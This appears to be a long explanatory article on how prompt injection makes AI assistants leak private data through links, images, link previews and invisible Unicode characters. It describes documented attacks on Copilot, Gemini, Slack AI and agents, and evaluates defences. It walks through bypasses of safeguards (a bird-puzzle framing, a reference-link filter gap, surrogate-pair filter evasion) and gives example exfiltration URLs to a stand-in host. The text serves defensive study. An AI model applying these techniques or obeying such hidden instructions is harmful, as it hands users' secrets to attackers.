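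The hidden order to disregard earlier instructions had mixed effects. Claude Opus 4 and GPT-5.2 complied less often than they did with the plain wording (23.9% against 32.0% and 6.1% against 11.8%, respectively), but Claude Sonnet 4 complied more often (59.6% against 43.7%). Graves thinks the forceful wording may have made Sonnet more likely to comply. But the comparison isn't quite fair, because the forceful wording always came with the full decoding rules, while the figures for the plain wording seem to include the runs without hints, which nearly always failed. The rules alone might explain Sonnet's increase.

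The grading is also approximate. Only 62% to 90% of answers were marked correct when there was no hidden text, partly because the grading misjudged long ones.

Graves points out that an attacker who controls only an email or a web page can't add hints to the system prompt. The low rates without hints therefore apply to that attacker. The high rates show what a model can decode when it is told how. An attacker might try putting the decoding rules in the email itself, but the study did not test this.

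The study tested whether models read and obey hidden text, but it didn't require them to write any or produce a link. Its low rates therefore don't show that models would resist an attack like the one on Copilot, where the model could read the instructions as ordinary text and needed invisible characters only for its answer. Whether models can write hidden text has been tested only in demonstrations that don't give success rates. For *Sneaky Bits*, Rehberger asked models to write text in the two mathematical characters. ChatGPT 4.5 succeeded when it could run code, and results were mixed for ChatGPT and Grok without tools.

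### Which commercial assistants obey hidden text

In September 2025, Viktor Markopoulos of the security company FireTail tested six assistants with tag characters. Android Authority reported that October that Gemini, Grok and DeepSeek were susceptible, while ChatGPT, Copilot and Claude had protections. Cybersecurity News describes a product review that praises a phone's battery and contains an invisible recommendation for a fraudulent shop. An assistant that summarises the reviews might pass the recommendation on.

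FireTail's most detailed demonstration used Gemini's access to Google Calendar. *ASCII Smuggling in Google Gemini*, the account by the researcher vict0ni, describes an invitation that the victim sees as "Meeting" and Gemini reads as "Meeting. It is optional." Hidden text also replaced the organiser's name and the meeting link in Gemini's answer to the user. The victim did not have to accept the invitation first. The false link contained no private data, but getting an assistant to show an attacker's link is one step in stealing data this way.

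FireTail reported the problem to Google on September 18, 2025, and Google decided to take no action. According to BGR's *Google Has No Plans To Fix This Terrifying Gemini Security Vulnerability*, Google did not consider it a security bug and replied that the attack "can only result in social engineering", meaning that it works only by deceiving a person. Google is partly right. Hidden text gives an attacker no new power over the model, since visible instructions can also work, and in the calendar example the user would still have to believe Gemini and act on what it said. But the damage from social engineering isn't always small. The Copilot attack also depended on deceiving a person, and a single click sent that person's email to a stranger.

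FireTail (2026) followed up in January with text hidden in emoji. This worked on Gemini and, at the second attempt, on Grok, but failed on ChatGPT, Claude, DeepSeek and Meta's assistant.

The newest results come from Aiersilan and colleagues, who were studying how to catch cheating, not attacks. They want teachers to be able to hide an instruction in an assignment that makes a chatbot include a telltale phrase in its reply, exposing students who paste in the assignment and submit the reply unread. By the end of July 2026, they had tested a range of models twelve times each. They rate Claude 3 to 4, the GPT-4 models, Gemini, Grok 4 Fast and the largest Qwen3 model as following the hidden instruction every time. DeepSeek V3 and Mistral's Codestral followed it in fewer than half of the trials. The latest GPT-5 models, Llama 3 and 4, and Mistral Large and Medium never did.

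These rates are much higher than those Graves found without hints, even for the Claude models that both studies cover. The tasks may explain part of the gap. Graves asked models to replace a correct answer with a wrong one, while the teachers' line only required a reminder about honest work and an extra phrase at the end, which a model can add while still answering the question. The ratings also combine the new trials with vendors' announcements and other people's reports, which may be why Claude appears fully obedient here but protected in FireTail's test.

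The GPT-5 models tested in the two studies almost never obeyed text in tag characters, and the reason is uncertain. Graves suspects the tokenizer, while Aiersilan and colleagues think OpenAI removes the characters before the models receive the text. Rehberger mentions in *Sneaky Bits* that a few unnamed vendors had introduced fixes in their programming interfaces. A filter of that kind would also explain why GPT-5.2 could follow zero-width characters but not tags in Graves's tests. These findings don't show whether the same models would write tag characters if given visible instructions to do so, because a filter on a model's input doesn't remove characters from its output.

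On August 5, 2026, Aiersilan and colleagues tested what a student could do to prevent the trick. With no precautions, Grok 4.5, Gemini 3.1 Pro and Gemini 3.6 Flash each obeyed the hidden line in all six trials. Telling the model to treat the pasted text as data, or to ignore instructions in it, nearly always prevented this. When the visible prompt instead asked for an answer with no reminders and no closing line, the smaller Gemini 3.6 Flash followed that request every time, but Grok still obeyed the hidden text in five of six trials and Gemini 3.1 Pro in all six. In its displayed reasoning, Grok noted that the two instructions conflicted and chose the invisible one.

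Two other models behaved differently in their chat products. GPT-5.6 Sol did not react to the hidden text. Claude Opus 5 read it but did not obey it, and began its reply by telling the user that the message contained hidden characters and describing the instructions in them.

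## Requests made without a click, and attacks that begin with one

The 2024 attacks on Slack AI and Copilot failed if the user didn't click the link. Not clicking doesn't protect the user if software opens the link first, and many messaging apps open links automatically.

### How a link preview sends the data

Suppose a user asks an assistant, through the messaging app Telegram, to summarise the day's email. One of the emails contains an attacker's instructions, and the assistant's answer includes a link to `https://garden.example/guides?c=482913`. The six digits are a login code from the mailbox. When the assistant's software posts the answer in the chat, Telegram finds the link and requests the page so that it can show a title, a description and a small picture under the message. The request includes the query string, so garden.example now has the code in its log, even if the user has not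 yet seen the message.

A request made without a click is much better for the attacker, because nobody has to be fooled. The link needs no pretext, and the attacker has no reason to hide the data in invisible characters.

Link previews are older than AI agents, and they were mostly harmless when a person had chosen each link. The day after PromptArmor published its attack on Slack AI, Willison (2024) described the problem that arises when a chatbot with access to private data can also post links, in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*. ("Unfurling" a link means generating a preview of it.) He named Slack and Discord as apps that preview links, and wrote that he hadn't thought of the problem before.

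### The test with OpenClaw and Telegram

In February 2026 PromptArmor tested how often this happens in practice. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* focuses on OpenClaw, an AI agent that people run themselves and instruct through apps such as Telegram and Slack. With OpenClaw's default Telegram settings, previews were on and the data leaked as soon as the agent replied.

The company also set up a website where people could test their own agents. A visitor had an agent post a link to the site, and the site recorded whether a preview request arrived and what data came with it. One published log contains a name and an API key. The site tracked which preview programs made the most requests, Slack's and Telegram's among them, and visitors could report which combinations of agent and app had or had not produced a request. Since visitors chose what to test, the counts can show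 that a combination leaks but not how common leaks are among agents. PromptArmor believes that many other agents have the same problem.

OpenClaw users can turn previews off by adding `linkPreview: false` to the Telegram section of the agent's configuration file. When PromptArmor did this, the test site stopped receiving data. Slack developers can turn previews off by setting `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media` to false when their program posts a message, a precaution that Willison credits to Rehberger.

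These settings are the kind of deterministic safeguard that David C recommends. They also apply at a step the agent's software controls, since it must post a message before anyone can preview it. But somebody has to know about them and change them for each app. PromptArmor would like messaging companies to let people turn previews off for a single chat or channel, which would make it safer for an agent to post there. Even with previews off, the user can still click the link.

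Security scanners might cause the same leak. Some mail and chat systems open links to look for malware, and any program that requests the full address sends the attacker the data in it. A scanner that only compares the domain with a list of dangerous sites would send the attacker nothing. One that checks only incoming email would not see a link in a chat window, though it might open the link if the user emailed the answer to a colleague. This is an inference from how web requests work, since PromptArmor tested link previews, not scanners.

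### A link that leads into the assistant

Security researchers also use "one-click" for attacks that work differently from the one on Slack AI, where the click itself sent the data out. In three attacks that the data security company Varonis published in 2026, the user clicks a link that opens the assistant. The link's address contains a prompt, which the assistant carries out, and the data then leaves by another path. The attacker writes the whole address in advance, so it contains no private data.

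These attacks rely on a feature of many AI services, which accept a prompt in the query string of their own web address, usually in a parameter named `q`. In an example from Varonis' *Reprompt*, an address ending in `?q=Hello` opens Microsoft's Copilot and submits "Hello" as if the user had typed it and pressed Enter. An attacker can put a much longer prompt there and send the link by email or chat. Varonis calls this parameter-to-prompt injection.

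Training a model to distrust retrieved text would not obviously help against this attack, because the attacker's text arrives where the user's own message should be, not in an email the assistant has retrieved. Checking the domain doesn't help either, because the link does lead to Microsoft. A careful user might still notice an unusually long query string.

### Reprompt

In January 2026, Varonis disclosed Reprompt, an attack that worked against Copilot Personal, the consumer version of Microsoft's assistant. Copilot could request web pages while answering a question. The attack used a link containing a prompt that told Copilot to put personal data in a web address on the attacker's server and request that address.

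Copilot had safeguards against this. It usually refused to open an address without a good reason, and it could remove sensitive data from an address before requesting it. The researchers got past the refusal by presenting the task as a puzzle about a picture of a bird. Copilot removed sensitive data only from the first request, so they told it to do everything twice. In a test with a made-up secret phrase, Copilot removed the phrase the first time and sent it the second time. Varonis suspects that Microsoft limited the check to save time.

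Unlike a user's click, these requests came from Copilot itself, so Microsoft's software could have checked every one. It did not achieve complete mediation because it checked only the first request.

The attacker's server could also answer each request with a new instruction. In the demonstration, it requested the user's local time, then their location, then any information Copilot had about them, and finally a summary of their last conversation. Anyone who inspected the original link would have seen only the opening prompt, not these later requests. The exchange continued after the user closed the chat. Ars Technica's *A single click mounted a covert, multistage attack against Copilot* (2026) reports that the researchers obtained the target's name, location and details of events from the chat history.

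According to The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox*, Varonis reported Reprompt in August 2025 and Microsoft patched it in January 2026. Reprompt did not affect Microsoft 365 Copilot.

### SearchLeak

Five months later, Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) showed that a prompt in a link also worked against Copilot Enterprise Search, the business product that searches an organisation's emails, meetings and files. The prompt told Copilot to find an email and put its title into the address of an image.

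Microsoft had anticipated this kind of dangerous output. Its software wrapped Copilot's answers in code blocks, which make a browser show HTML as text instead of acting on it. But the software wrapped each answer only after it was complete. Copilot's answers appear on the screen piece by piece, so the browser found the image tag and requested the image while the answer was still arriving.

The page's Content Security Policy, which limits where the browser can load images from, would have blocked an image on the attackers' server. But it allowed images from Bing, Microsoft's search engine, which has a feature that fetches an image from a given address for analysis. The attackers therefore used an image address that pointed to Bing and contained a second address, on their own server, with the email's title in the path. When the browser requested the image from Bing, Bing requested the second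 address from the attackers' server. The policy did not block that request because it does not apply to Bing's servers.

The published demonstration took an email subject line that included a security code. Since Copilot has the same access as the user, Varonis warns that an attacker could also have obtained the text of emails, password-reset links, meeting notes, and files in SharePoint and OneDrive, Microsoft's document storage services. The files might include salary lists or acquisition plans.

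Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), the official record of the flaw, appeared on June 4, eleven days before Varonis published its account. Microsoft wrote that it had already fully mitigated the problem and that customers didn't need to do anything. The record lists no known exploitation and includes no explanation of the fix. Varonis advises other developers to clean an answer as it renders and to look for any permitted domain that will fetch an address on request.

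### CoSnitch

The third attack, again on Copilot Personal, became public in August 2026. Varonis' *CoSnitch* says the researchers found the weakness by questioning Copilot about itself. When Copilot refused a request, they used its explanation to decide what to try next. TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions* reports that this eventually led them to a URL format that ran a prompt as soon as the page opened. The URL combined the `q` parameter with an undocumented one.

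The data left through Copilot's built-in ability to fetch web addresses, according to the device-management company Hexnode. At first the researchers could take only what the victim had told Copilot in earlier sessions. If the victim had connected Gmail, Google Drive or Google Calendar, the prompt could also reach the data there, including any passwords in the text of emails.

CoSnitch also included a flaw that allowed ordinary indirect prompt injection without a special link. An attacker could prepare a web page that put instructions into Copilot's permanent memory of the user when Copilot summarised it. These instructions remained after the user changed their password.

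Varonis reported CoSnitch in December 2025, and Microsoft patched it on August 18, 2026, more than eight months later. The fix was on Microsoft's servers, so users had nothing to install. TechRadar notes that Microsoft did not reveal what it had changed and that Varonis found no evidence of abuse.

### How a required click lowers a severity score

Microsoft gave SearchLeak a severity score of 6.5 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5. Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails, MFA Codes* (2026) explains that the two disagreed about whether the attack needed the user to do anything.

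Both used version 3.1 of the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS). For a flaw like this one, the score is the sum of an impact figure and an exploitability figure, rounded up to one decimal place. Microsoft and the NVD agreed that SearchLeak could expose a great deal of confidential data but not alter data or interrupt the service. They also agreed that an attacker could carry it out over the internet, without difficulty and without an account. With the standard weights for those answers, the formula becomes:

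impact = 6.42 × 0.56 = 3.60

exploitability = 8.22 × 0.85 × 0.77 × 0.85 × u = 4.57 × u

The value of u is 0.62 if the victim has to take part and 0.85 if not.

| Rating | u | Exploitability | Impact + exploitability | Score |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Microsoft: user interaction required | 0.62 | 2.84 | 6.43 | 6.5 (medium) |
| NVD: no user interaction | 0.85 | 3.89 | 7.48 | 7.5 (high) |

One click therefore accounts for the whole difference. Microsoft's other ratings follow the same pattern. In May 2026, Microsoft published a different Copilot flaw with the same ratings, except that it required no user interaction. Lutra Security (2026) lists its score as 7.5.

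On the facts that Varonis published, Microsoft was right, because the victim had to click the link. The NVD's reason is less clear. CVEfeed's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), which logs changes to the entry, dates the second rating to June 8, a week before Varonis explained the attack. The NVD works from public information, and Microsoft's one-sentence description did not mention a link. NIST's *CVSS v3.1 Statistics for GitHub, Inc* (2026), from the agency that runs the database, includes another case in which an analyst chose a different value "due to lack of available Information". That may have happened here too, although Microsoft's own rating already said that the attack needed the user. (The Next Web reported that the NVD also gave 6.5, but the change log contradicts this.)

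The CVSS score doesn't account for how likely a user is to click. A link on a genuine Microsoft domain gets the same 0.62 as one that almost nobody would trust. An attack that requires a click can still score high. CoSnitch also required a click and scored 8.8, perhaps partly because the attacker could also change what Copilot remembered, and CVSS counts altered data as well as stolen data. Microsoft rated SearchLeak "Critical" on its own severity scale, which is separate from CVSS.

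Link previews make this part of the score harder to apply. If an attacker tricks an assistant into showing a link that contains private data, the user has to click the link for the data to leak on the assistant's own website, but not in a Telegram chat with previews on. If everything else matched SearchLeak, the same weakness would score 6.5 on the website and 7.5 in Telegram, so a developer who tested only the website would choose the lower score.

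### ReLeak and the routes that involve no clicked link

On December 3, 2026, *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) disclosed three zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot. Simonovich wrote it for Cato AI Labs, the research group of a network security company. Some of the group's researchers had found EchoLeak, an earlier zero-click attack on Copilot.

All three attacks began with an email that the victim never had to open. As Faisal (2026), in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*, explains, Copilot retrieved the email when the user asked an ordinary work question, and then followed the instructions in it. Microsoft's protections against prompt injection blocked none of the three. The data left in different ways:

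- Copilot put the data in an image address, and Bing passed it on to the attacker's server when the browser loaded the image.
- Copilot saved a Word, Excel, PowerPoint or PDF file containing a link with the data in its address. Microsoft's background processing later accessed the file, and the data went out.
- Copilot ran Python code that sent the data directly to an outside server, although the environment for running code was supposed to have no network access.

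Cato reported the flaws between July 29 and August 20. Microsoft fixed the Python route on September 17, the saved files on November 11 and the Bing images on November 15. Cato knows of no real attacks that used them.

All three attacks would still have worked if Copilot had removed every clickable link from its chat answers. The saved-file attack is the most similar to the 2024 attacks on Slack AI and Copilot because it also put the data in an ordinary link, but Microsoft's own software sent the request that had previously required a user's click. A warning triggered by a click would never have appeared.

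The Bing route also suggests that these paths are hard to close one at a time. Microsoft declared SearchLeak fully mitigated in early June, and within three months Cato reported another attack in which Bing carried data from Copilot to an outside server.

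## Removing hidden characters and links from answers

Before showing an answer, an application can delete invisible characters, so that a link can't carry data the user can't see, and it can remove or disable the links themselves. Ordinary code does both, so neither depends on the model recognising an attack. But the code has to interpret the answer the same way as the program that displays it, and several filters have failed because they didn't.

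### Where to filter invisible characters

An assistant can filter the text that goes into the model, the text that comes out, or both. An input filter removes hidden instructions. Embrace The Red's *Amazon Q Developer for VS Code Vulnerable to Invisible Prompt Injection* (2025) describes a coding assistant that followed instructions written in tag characters. Amazon reported the problem resolved on August 8, 2025. In Rehberger's attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, the model wrote the tag characters itself, so only a filter on the answer would have removed them.

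An output filter also has to check inside link addresses, where the same character can take several forms. A model could write a hidden digit 4 as the tag character U+E0034, as the percent-encoded bytes `%F3%A0%80%B4`, or as the numeric code `&#xE0034;`, which Markdown and HTML convert to the character. The last two contain only visible characters, so a search for tag characters misses them, but the browser may decode them and show an address that seems to end early. Running the filter after the software has interpreted the Markdown, and decoding each address before checking it, is safer. The bytes are easy to recognise because the whole block runs from F3 A0 80 80 to F3 A0 81 BF, according to Cisco's *Understanding and Mitigating Unicode Tag Prompt Injection*.

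The filter must also finish before the text appears. Copilot's protection against SearchLeak ran too late because Copilot was already displaying the answer piece by piece. An application that displays answers this way has to hold back each link until it has the complete address.

### Sequences that survive a single pass

A filter can delete every tag character it finds and still leave one behind. AWS's *Defending LLM applications against Unicode character smuggling*, from Amazon's cloud computing business, explains how this happens in the programming language Java. Java stores text in units of 16 bits. The code point of a tag character is too large for one unit, so Java uses two, called a high surrogate and a low surrogate. The pair for the tag character U+E0001 is DB40 DC01. An attacker can put one such pair inside another:

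`DB40 DB40 DC01 DC01`

Java reads the middle two units as a tag character and the outer two as unpaired surrogates. When the filter deletes the middle pair, the outer two become adjacent and form a new U+E0001.

AWS's corrected code also deletes stray surrogates, and it repeats the process until the text stops changing. Either change would defeat this sequence. In Python the surrogates don't merge, so one pass is enough, but AWS removes stray ones there too because some models can recombine adjacent surrogates. An attacker could separate them with other characters and tell the model to ignore those, but AWS notes that the text would then be visible.

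These filters are easy to get slightly wrong. AWS's Java code for removing stray surrogates checks only the last 16 bits of each code point, so it also deletes 2,048 rare Chinese characters between U+2D800 and U+2DFFF. AWS also offers customers of its Guardrails service a rule that blocks a whole prompt or answer instead of cleaning it. AWS's example surrogate pairs for this rule, such as DB40 DD41, stand for variation selectors, not tag characters.

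### What to remove and what it breaks

Many programs run a Unicode clean-up step called NFKC normalisation, which replaces variant forms of a character with a standard one. trackr.live's *Invisible Unicode Tags Smuggle Instructions Past Your LLM Filter* warns that this doesn't remove tag characters, so developers have to filter out that range of characters explicitly. A filter for tags alone misses text written in variation selectors or in two invisible characters that stand for 0 and 1. trackr.live's *Unicode Tag Smuggling Is Prompt Injection With a Byte Signature* adds zero-width characters and controls that change text direction to the characters to filter.

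Removing all tag characters turns the flags of England, Scotland and Wales into plain black flags, which AWS thinks most businesses can accept. An application could prevent this by keeping the three exact sequences that produce these flags and deleting every other tag character.

The other invisible characters have more legitimate uses, but a filter can be stricter inside a link address, which rarely needs emoji. The stricter filter would still break some legitimate links. For example, Persian spelling uses the zero-width non-joiner, so a web address made from a Persian page title may contain one.

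Even a filter that removed every hidden character could still let the same data through as visible text. Software could search that text for private data, but it would have to recognise the data in every encoding. In a post about encoded text, AWS gives the example of a rule against discussing Amazon's stock, which a user might get around by writing "amazon" in base64 as "YW1hem9u".

### Four ways to treat a link

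If the application removes the link, the encoding of the data inside it no longer matters. Several weaker treatments keep links partly usable.

| Treatment | What it stops | How data can still leave | Cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| No addresses at all | Clicking and copying | Images, saved files and other routes | Users can't open sources from the answer |
| Address as plain text | Clicks in the assistant's window | The user copies the address, or another program makes it clickable | An extra step for every source |
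| Clickable, with the full address shown | Hiding the destination behind friendly words | The user clicks anyway | Long, cluttered answers |
| Clickable only for listed domains | Direct visits to an attacker's server | Redirects and other services on listed sites | Most of the web is not on the list |

Amazon chose the strictest treatment for Amazon Q for Business, and Microsoft's 2024 fix for Copilot seems to have included something similar. The main loss is citations, but an application can restore many of them. Its search software can attach links to the documents it added to the context, without the model writing any address. A user who asks for a shop's website would still get no link.

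Showing links as plain text protects users less than it seems to. An attacker who can persuade someone to click a link to renew an expired session can probably persuade them to copy it into the browser. Many email and chat programs also turn anything that looks like a web address into a link, so the protection may end when the user forwards the answer to a colleague. Some Markdown software does the same, in which case the address stays clickable even after the link's brackets are removed. Security analysts avoid this problem by putting brackets around the dots in a dangerous address, which stops most programs from recognising it.

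Showing the full address would have exposed the key in the Slack AI demonstration, but not the invisible text in Rehberger's attack on Copilot. An application that relies on this defense should therefore show addresses in percent-encoded form. Even then, the user must be able to tell stolen data from an ordinary tracking code.

### The link format that Copilot's filter missed

The first half of the EchoLeak attack produced a link for the user to click, although the attack is known as zero-click. *EchoLeak*, by Pavan Reddy and Aditya Sanjay Gujral of George Washington University, reconstructs the attack from published accounts rather than by reproducing it.

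The attack began with an email. Microsoft used a classifier to detect prompt injection, so the attackers worded their instructions as if they were meant for the human recipient. They also told Copilot not to mention the email, which kept it out of the answer.

Copilot was then supposed to write a link with sensitive data in its address. Its software removed ordinary Markdown links, in which the address comes straight after the visible words. But Markdown also allows a reference link, which gives the address on a separate line:

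```
[Umbrella sizes][guide]

[guide]: https://garden.example/guides?c=482913
```

The filter did not detect this form, but the program that displayed the answer turned it into a working link. One click by the user would have sent the data.

The attackers removed the need for a click by adding an exclamation mark to turn the link into an image. The page's Content Security Policy blocked images from unknown domains, but it allowed a Microsoft Teams service that generates previews by fetching whatever address it receives. The attackers put their own address inside a Teams address, and Microsoft's server passed the data on to them.

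Aim Labs found the attack in January 2025. Microsoft fixed the vulnerability on its servers in May and published an advisory on June 11. It had no evidence that anyone had used the attack.

Copilot's filter failed because it recognized fewer forms of link than the display software did. A filter that runs after the Markdown is parsed into a structured document avoids this problem, because inline and reference links look the same by then. *EchoLeak* recommends allowing only a small, safe subset of Markdown and dropping everything else. It also mentions that Microsoft began to strip reference links and images from incoming outside content, but that alone would not stop a model from writing a new reference link in its answer.

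The paper includes a table of which defences would stop which steps. It is a reasoned guess, since Reddy and Gujral ran no experiments.

### Why lists of trusted domains leak

A list of trusted domains would have blocked a direct link to the attacker's server in every attack described so far. The trouble is that a link can begin at a trusted site and end somewhere else. Suppose `shop.example` is on the list and has a page that forwards visitors to any address they supply:

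`https://shop.example/go?to=https%3A%2F%2Fgarden.example%2Fguides%3Fc%3D482913`

The host is `shop.example`, so the link passes the check. When the user clicks it, the shop's server redirects the browser to the address after `to=`, and the browser sends garden.example a request containing the login code. Security researchers call such a page an open redirect.

Large sites have redirects too. Embrace The Red reports that Google's programming notebook Colab puts `https://www.google.com/url?q=` in front of every clickable link in its AI assistant's answers. This brings up a confirmation page, which is useful in Colab, but it also lets an address on google.com lead to any site. If a list of allowed sites included all of google.com, the confirmation page would be the user's only protection.

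The application could follow each redirect before showing the link, as *EchoLeak* suggests. It would have to stop at the first unlisted address without requesting it, because the request itself would deliver the data. The listed site could still redirect the user later to a different address from the one it gave the checker.

Some listed sites leak data without redirecting anyone. If a list includes a service that hosts customers' pages or forms, an attacker can open an account there and may be able to read the addresses that visitors request. Some websites exist to show their users these requests, because developers need to see what their programs send. A listed site may also fetch other addresses on request, as Teams did in EchoLeak and Bing did in SearchLeak.

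Developers can limit the list to particular paths, or remove the query string from every permitted link. The second option breaks search results and many other pages that need the query string, and an attacker can still put the data in the path.

A short list of allowed sites could work well for a company assistant that only needs to link to the company's own documents. It is much less suitable for an assistant that searches the web. OpenAI warns that strict lists produce frequent false alarms, which teach people to click through warnings without thinking. OpenAI instead checks whether a link's exact address is already public.

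### What the Silent Egress experiment measured

*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) compared a domain list with several other defences. The researchers, who work at eBay, built an agent on their own computers with Qwen2.5 7B, a small open model. They gave the agent a tool for making web requests, put a secret in its context, and asked it to summarise a web page that contained instructions to send the secret to another server.

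Researchers hid instructions for an AI agent in four places on a web page, including its title and its description for search engines. In half the runs, the instructions told the agent to split a secret across four requests. The agent contacted the attacker's server in 423 of 480 runs (88%). The rate was 99% when it could send the secret in one request and 77% when it had to split it. In 120 control runs with harmless pages, the agent never contacted the server. In 95% of the successful attacks, the agent's written answer looked normal.

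The researchers then tested each defence in 30 runs, using the unsplit secret and instructions in the body of the page.

| Defence | Agent attempted a request (%) | Request reached the attacker (%) |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100 | 100 |
| System prompt forbids obeying web content | 66.7 | 66.7 |
| Tags mark web content as untrusted | 100 | 100 |
| Both of these | 56.7 | 56.7 |
| Domain list | 100 | 0 |
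| Block suspicious-looking addresses | 83.3 | 0 |
| Block words such as "secret" and "token" | 23.3 | 0 |
| Block random-looking values | 0 | 0 |
| All defences together | 0 | 0 |

The failure of the prompt-level defences is more informative than the domain list's perfect score, at least for this model. Marking the content as untrusted made no difference, and even the best combination failed in 17 of 30 runs. The domain list's score was almost guaranteed, because the list permitted four domains and the attacker's was deliberately left out. Lan and colleagues acknowledge that a real attacker could bypass the list through an open redirect, a hacked legitimate site, or an abandoned subdomain that an outsider can take over.

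The rule against suspicious-looking addresses has a similar weakness. It blocks certain words in the path, including "collect", and the paper's example attacks send data to `/collect`, but an attacker could choose another word.

The rule against random-looking values uses Shannon entropy, a measure of how varied the characters in a text are:

H = −Σ pᵢ log₂ pᵢ

Here pᵢ is the share of the text made up of the i-th distinct character. The rule blocks a value of more than 10 characters if H is above 4.0. Hexadecimal, the encoding in Logue's attack, uses 16 different characters, so its H is at most log₂ 16 = 4.0 and the rule never blocks it. The rule also never blocks a number, however long, because ten digits give an H of at most 3.32. The sample key in the paper, `SECRET_API_KEY_12345`, has an H of 3.85, so the rule doesn't block it either.

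It is therefore odd that the agent made no attempts when this rule was active. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoided random-looking values, but they don't explain how the model would have known about a rule that runs outside it. The figures for the two content filters are hard to rely on until someone repeats the test.

The experiment measured requests the agent made, not users' clicks. The results for prompts are still relevant to links because they concern whether a model obeys planted instructions. The network results don't apply to clicks, which bypass the agent's network filter. A company that also filters its employees' browsing could check the request in that browsing filter.

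### Why a Content Security Policy does not stop a click

The browser handles the click, so a browser rule could stop it, but Content Security Policy (CSP) controls what a page loads into itself. For example, Microsoft used CSP in May 2023 to stop Bing Chat from loading outside images, according to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*. A clicked link takes the user to a different page, and an early draft of the CSP standard, Mozilla's *Security/CSP/Spec*, states that preventing "navigation to arbitrary sites" was not the aim.

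Paicu (2018), in *Intent to implement and ship*, proposed a CSP rule for Chrome called `navigate-to`, which would have limited where a page could send the user by any means, including links. But the rule turned out to reveal whether a user was logged in to another site. An attacker's page could allow visits to a shop's account page but not its login page, then send the user to the account page. If the browser blocked the visit, the attacker could tell that the shop had redirected the user to the login page because they weren't logged in.

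The editors removed `navigate-to` from the draft standard in September 2022. Mozilla's *Remove (disabled by default) CSP directive `navigate-to`* gives leaks of this kind as the reason and says that no browser ever shipped the rule. A developer of Safari's engine, WebKit (2022), noted that Chrome's developers had built it behind an experimental setting and wanted it removed too.

A newer mechanism, which West proposes in *Connection Allowlists*, does cover clicked links. It is a separate list of every address that a page may contact. West, who works at Google and edits the CSP standard, argues that CSP sorts requests into too many types and still misses some, such as DNS prefetches. In a DNS prefetch, the browser looks up a site's host name before anyone visits the site, which could leak private data that an attacker had put in the host name.

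Chrome's *Connection Allowlists origin trial* (2026) confirms that the list applies to navigations and redirects. Helme explains in *Connection Allowlist* that the browser blocks all redirects unless the site allows them, because a server that receives a request controls where the browser goes next. This blocks the `shop.example` route by default. The feature reached all Chrome users in version 152, released on August 25 (Chrome, 2026).

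An assistant's website could now use this header to make Chrome block clicked links to unlisted servers. But when Chromium's *Intent to Experiment* (2026) appeared in March, the developers of Firefox and Safari had not said whether they would adopt the feature. The header also applies only to web pages, so it doesn't automatically protect someone who clicks a link in a desktop or phone app.

A user who copies a link and pastes it into a new tab would also bypass the list of permitted addresses, because the check applied only to navigations started by the page. In a code review for Chrome, Sharma (2026) discusses tests that treat these differently from navigations started by the browser itself. A web search assistant's list would also have to include every site it might cite.

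### Google's removal of suspicious addresses

Google's assistant Gemini keeps most links and removes the ones that look dangerous. According to Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025), Gemini doesn't display images from outside addresses. It also checks web addresses with a system based on Safe Browsing, Google's service for identifying dangerous sites. If a user asks for a summary of a document that contains a malicious address, the summary shows "suspicious link removed" in place of the address.

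*Google Workspace's continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* (Gavish, 2026) adds that a central policy engine controls this step. When Google learns of a new attack, it can change the engine's settings to block a particular pattern, which is faster than retraining a model. Google tests its defences by running simulated attacks with and without them, but neither post reports how many harmful links the address check catches.

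Tenable's *The Trifecta* found that Gemini also redirected Markdown links through a google.com address and cut off some suspicious answers. Tenable's researchers then looked for a way to send data out through Gemini's tools, which a filter on the answer does not control.

The image rule did not protect every Gemini product. Google said in June 2025 that the rule prevented EchoLeak's image method from working in the Gemini app and in Gemini in Workspace, its office software. SC Media later reported that Noma Labs' GeminiJack attack on Gemini Enterprise, a separate product for businesses, put search results into the address of an image on the attacker's server.

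For clickable links, the main weakness is that Safe Browsing checks whether a site is dangerous, not whether an address contains private data. An attacker could register a new domain, put a harmless page on it, and use it only to record the addresses that visitors request. A reputation check would be unlikely to flag the site until somebody reported it. *Gemini Agent Security Risks*, a risk rating by the security company Adversa AI, lists data theft through links as an unfixed gap in Gemini, though a rating is weaker evidence than a published demonstration.

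## Allowing only addresses already known to be public

OpenAI's Safe Url method lets ChatGPT open an address automatically only if that exact address is already public on the web. The decision does not depend on the site's reputation, whereas Google checks whether the site behind a link is dangerous.

### How Safe Url works

OpenAI described the method in January 2026. The company runs a crawler, a program that scans public web pages and records the addresses it finds, much as a search engine does. The crawler has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data. When ChatGPT is about to open a page or load an image, software checks the address against the crawler's records. If there is an exact match, ChatGPT opens or loads it. If there isn't, the software either has the model try another website or warns the user before anything opens.

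The reasoning is that an address that existed before a conversation cannot have been written to contain secrets from that conversation. Suppose the crawler has recorded `https://garden.example/guides`, and an attacker's instructions make the model add `?c=482913`, a login code from the user's mailbox. The longer address leads to the same page on the same site, but the crawler has never recorded it, so ChatGPT won't open it automatically. An open redirect on a famous site also fails this test if someone has just added stolen data to its address.

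This defense works only if the crawler finds addresses independently of users' conversations. If OpenAI also recorded the addresses that users opened in ChatGPT, an address containing a user's login code could enter the records and then count as public. OpenAI says only that an address known independently of any conversation is "much less likely" to contain the user's private data.

According to OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (March 2026), the method applies to page visits and bookmarks in Atlas, OpenAI's web browser. It also applies to searches and page visits in Deep Research, a ChatGPT feature that reads many sources and writes a report. Canvas, where ChatGPT can build small applications, and ChatGPT Apps instead use a sandbox, an isolated environment that detects unexpected communication and asks the user for consent.

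OpenAI treats Safe Url as a backup. It writes that most attacks it knows of fail because the model refuses to take part. But the backup is still needed, since the same post reproduces a 2025 email attack that worked in half of the tests when the user asked for research on the day's emails.

### The earlier check and its gaps

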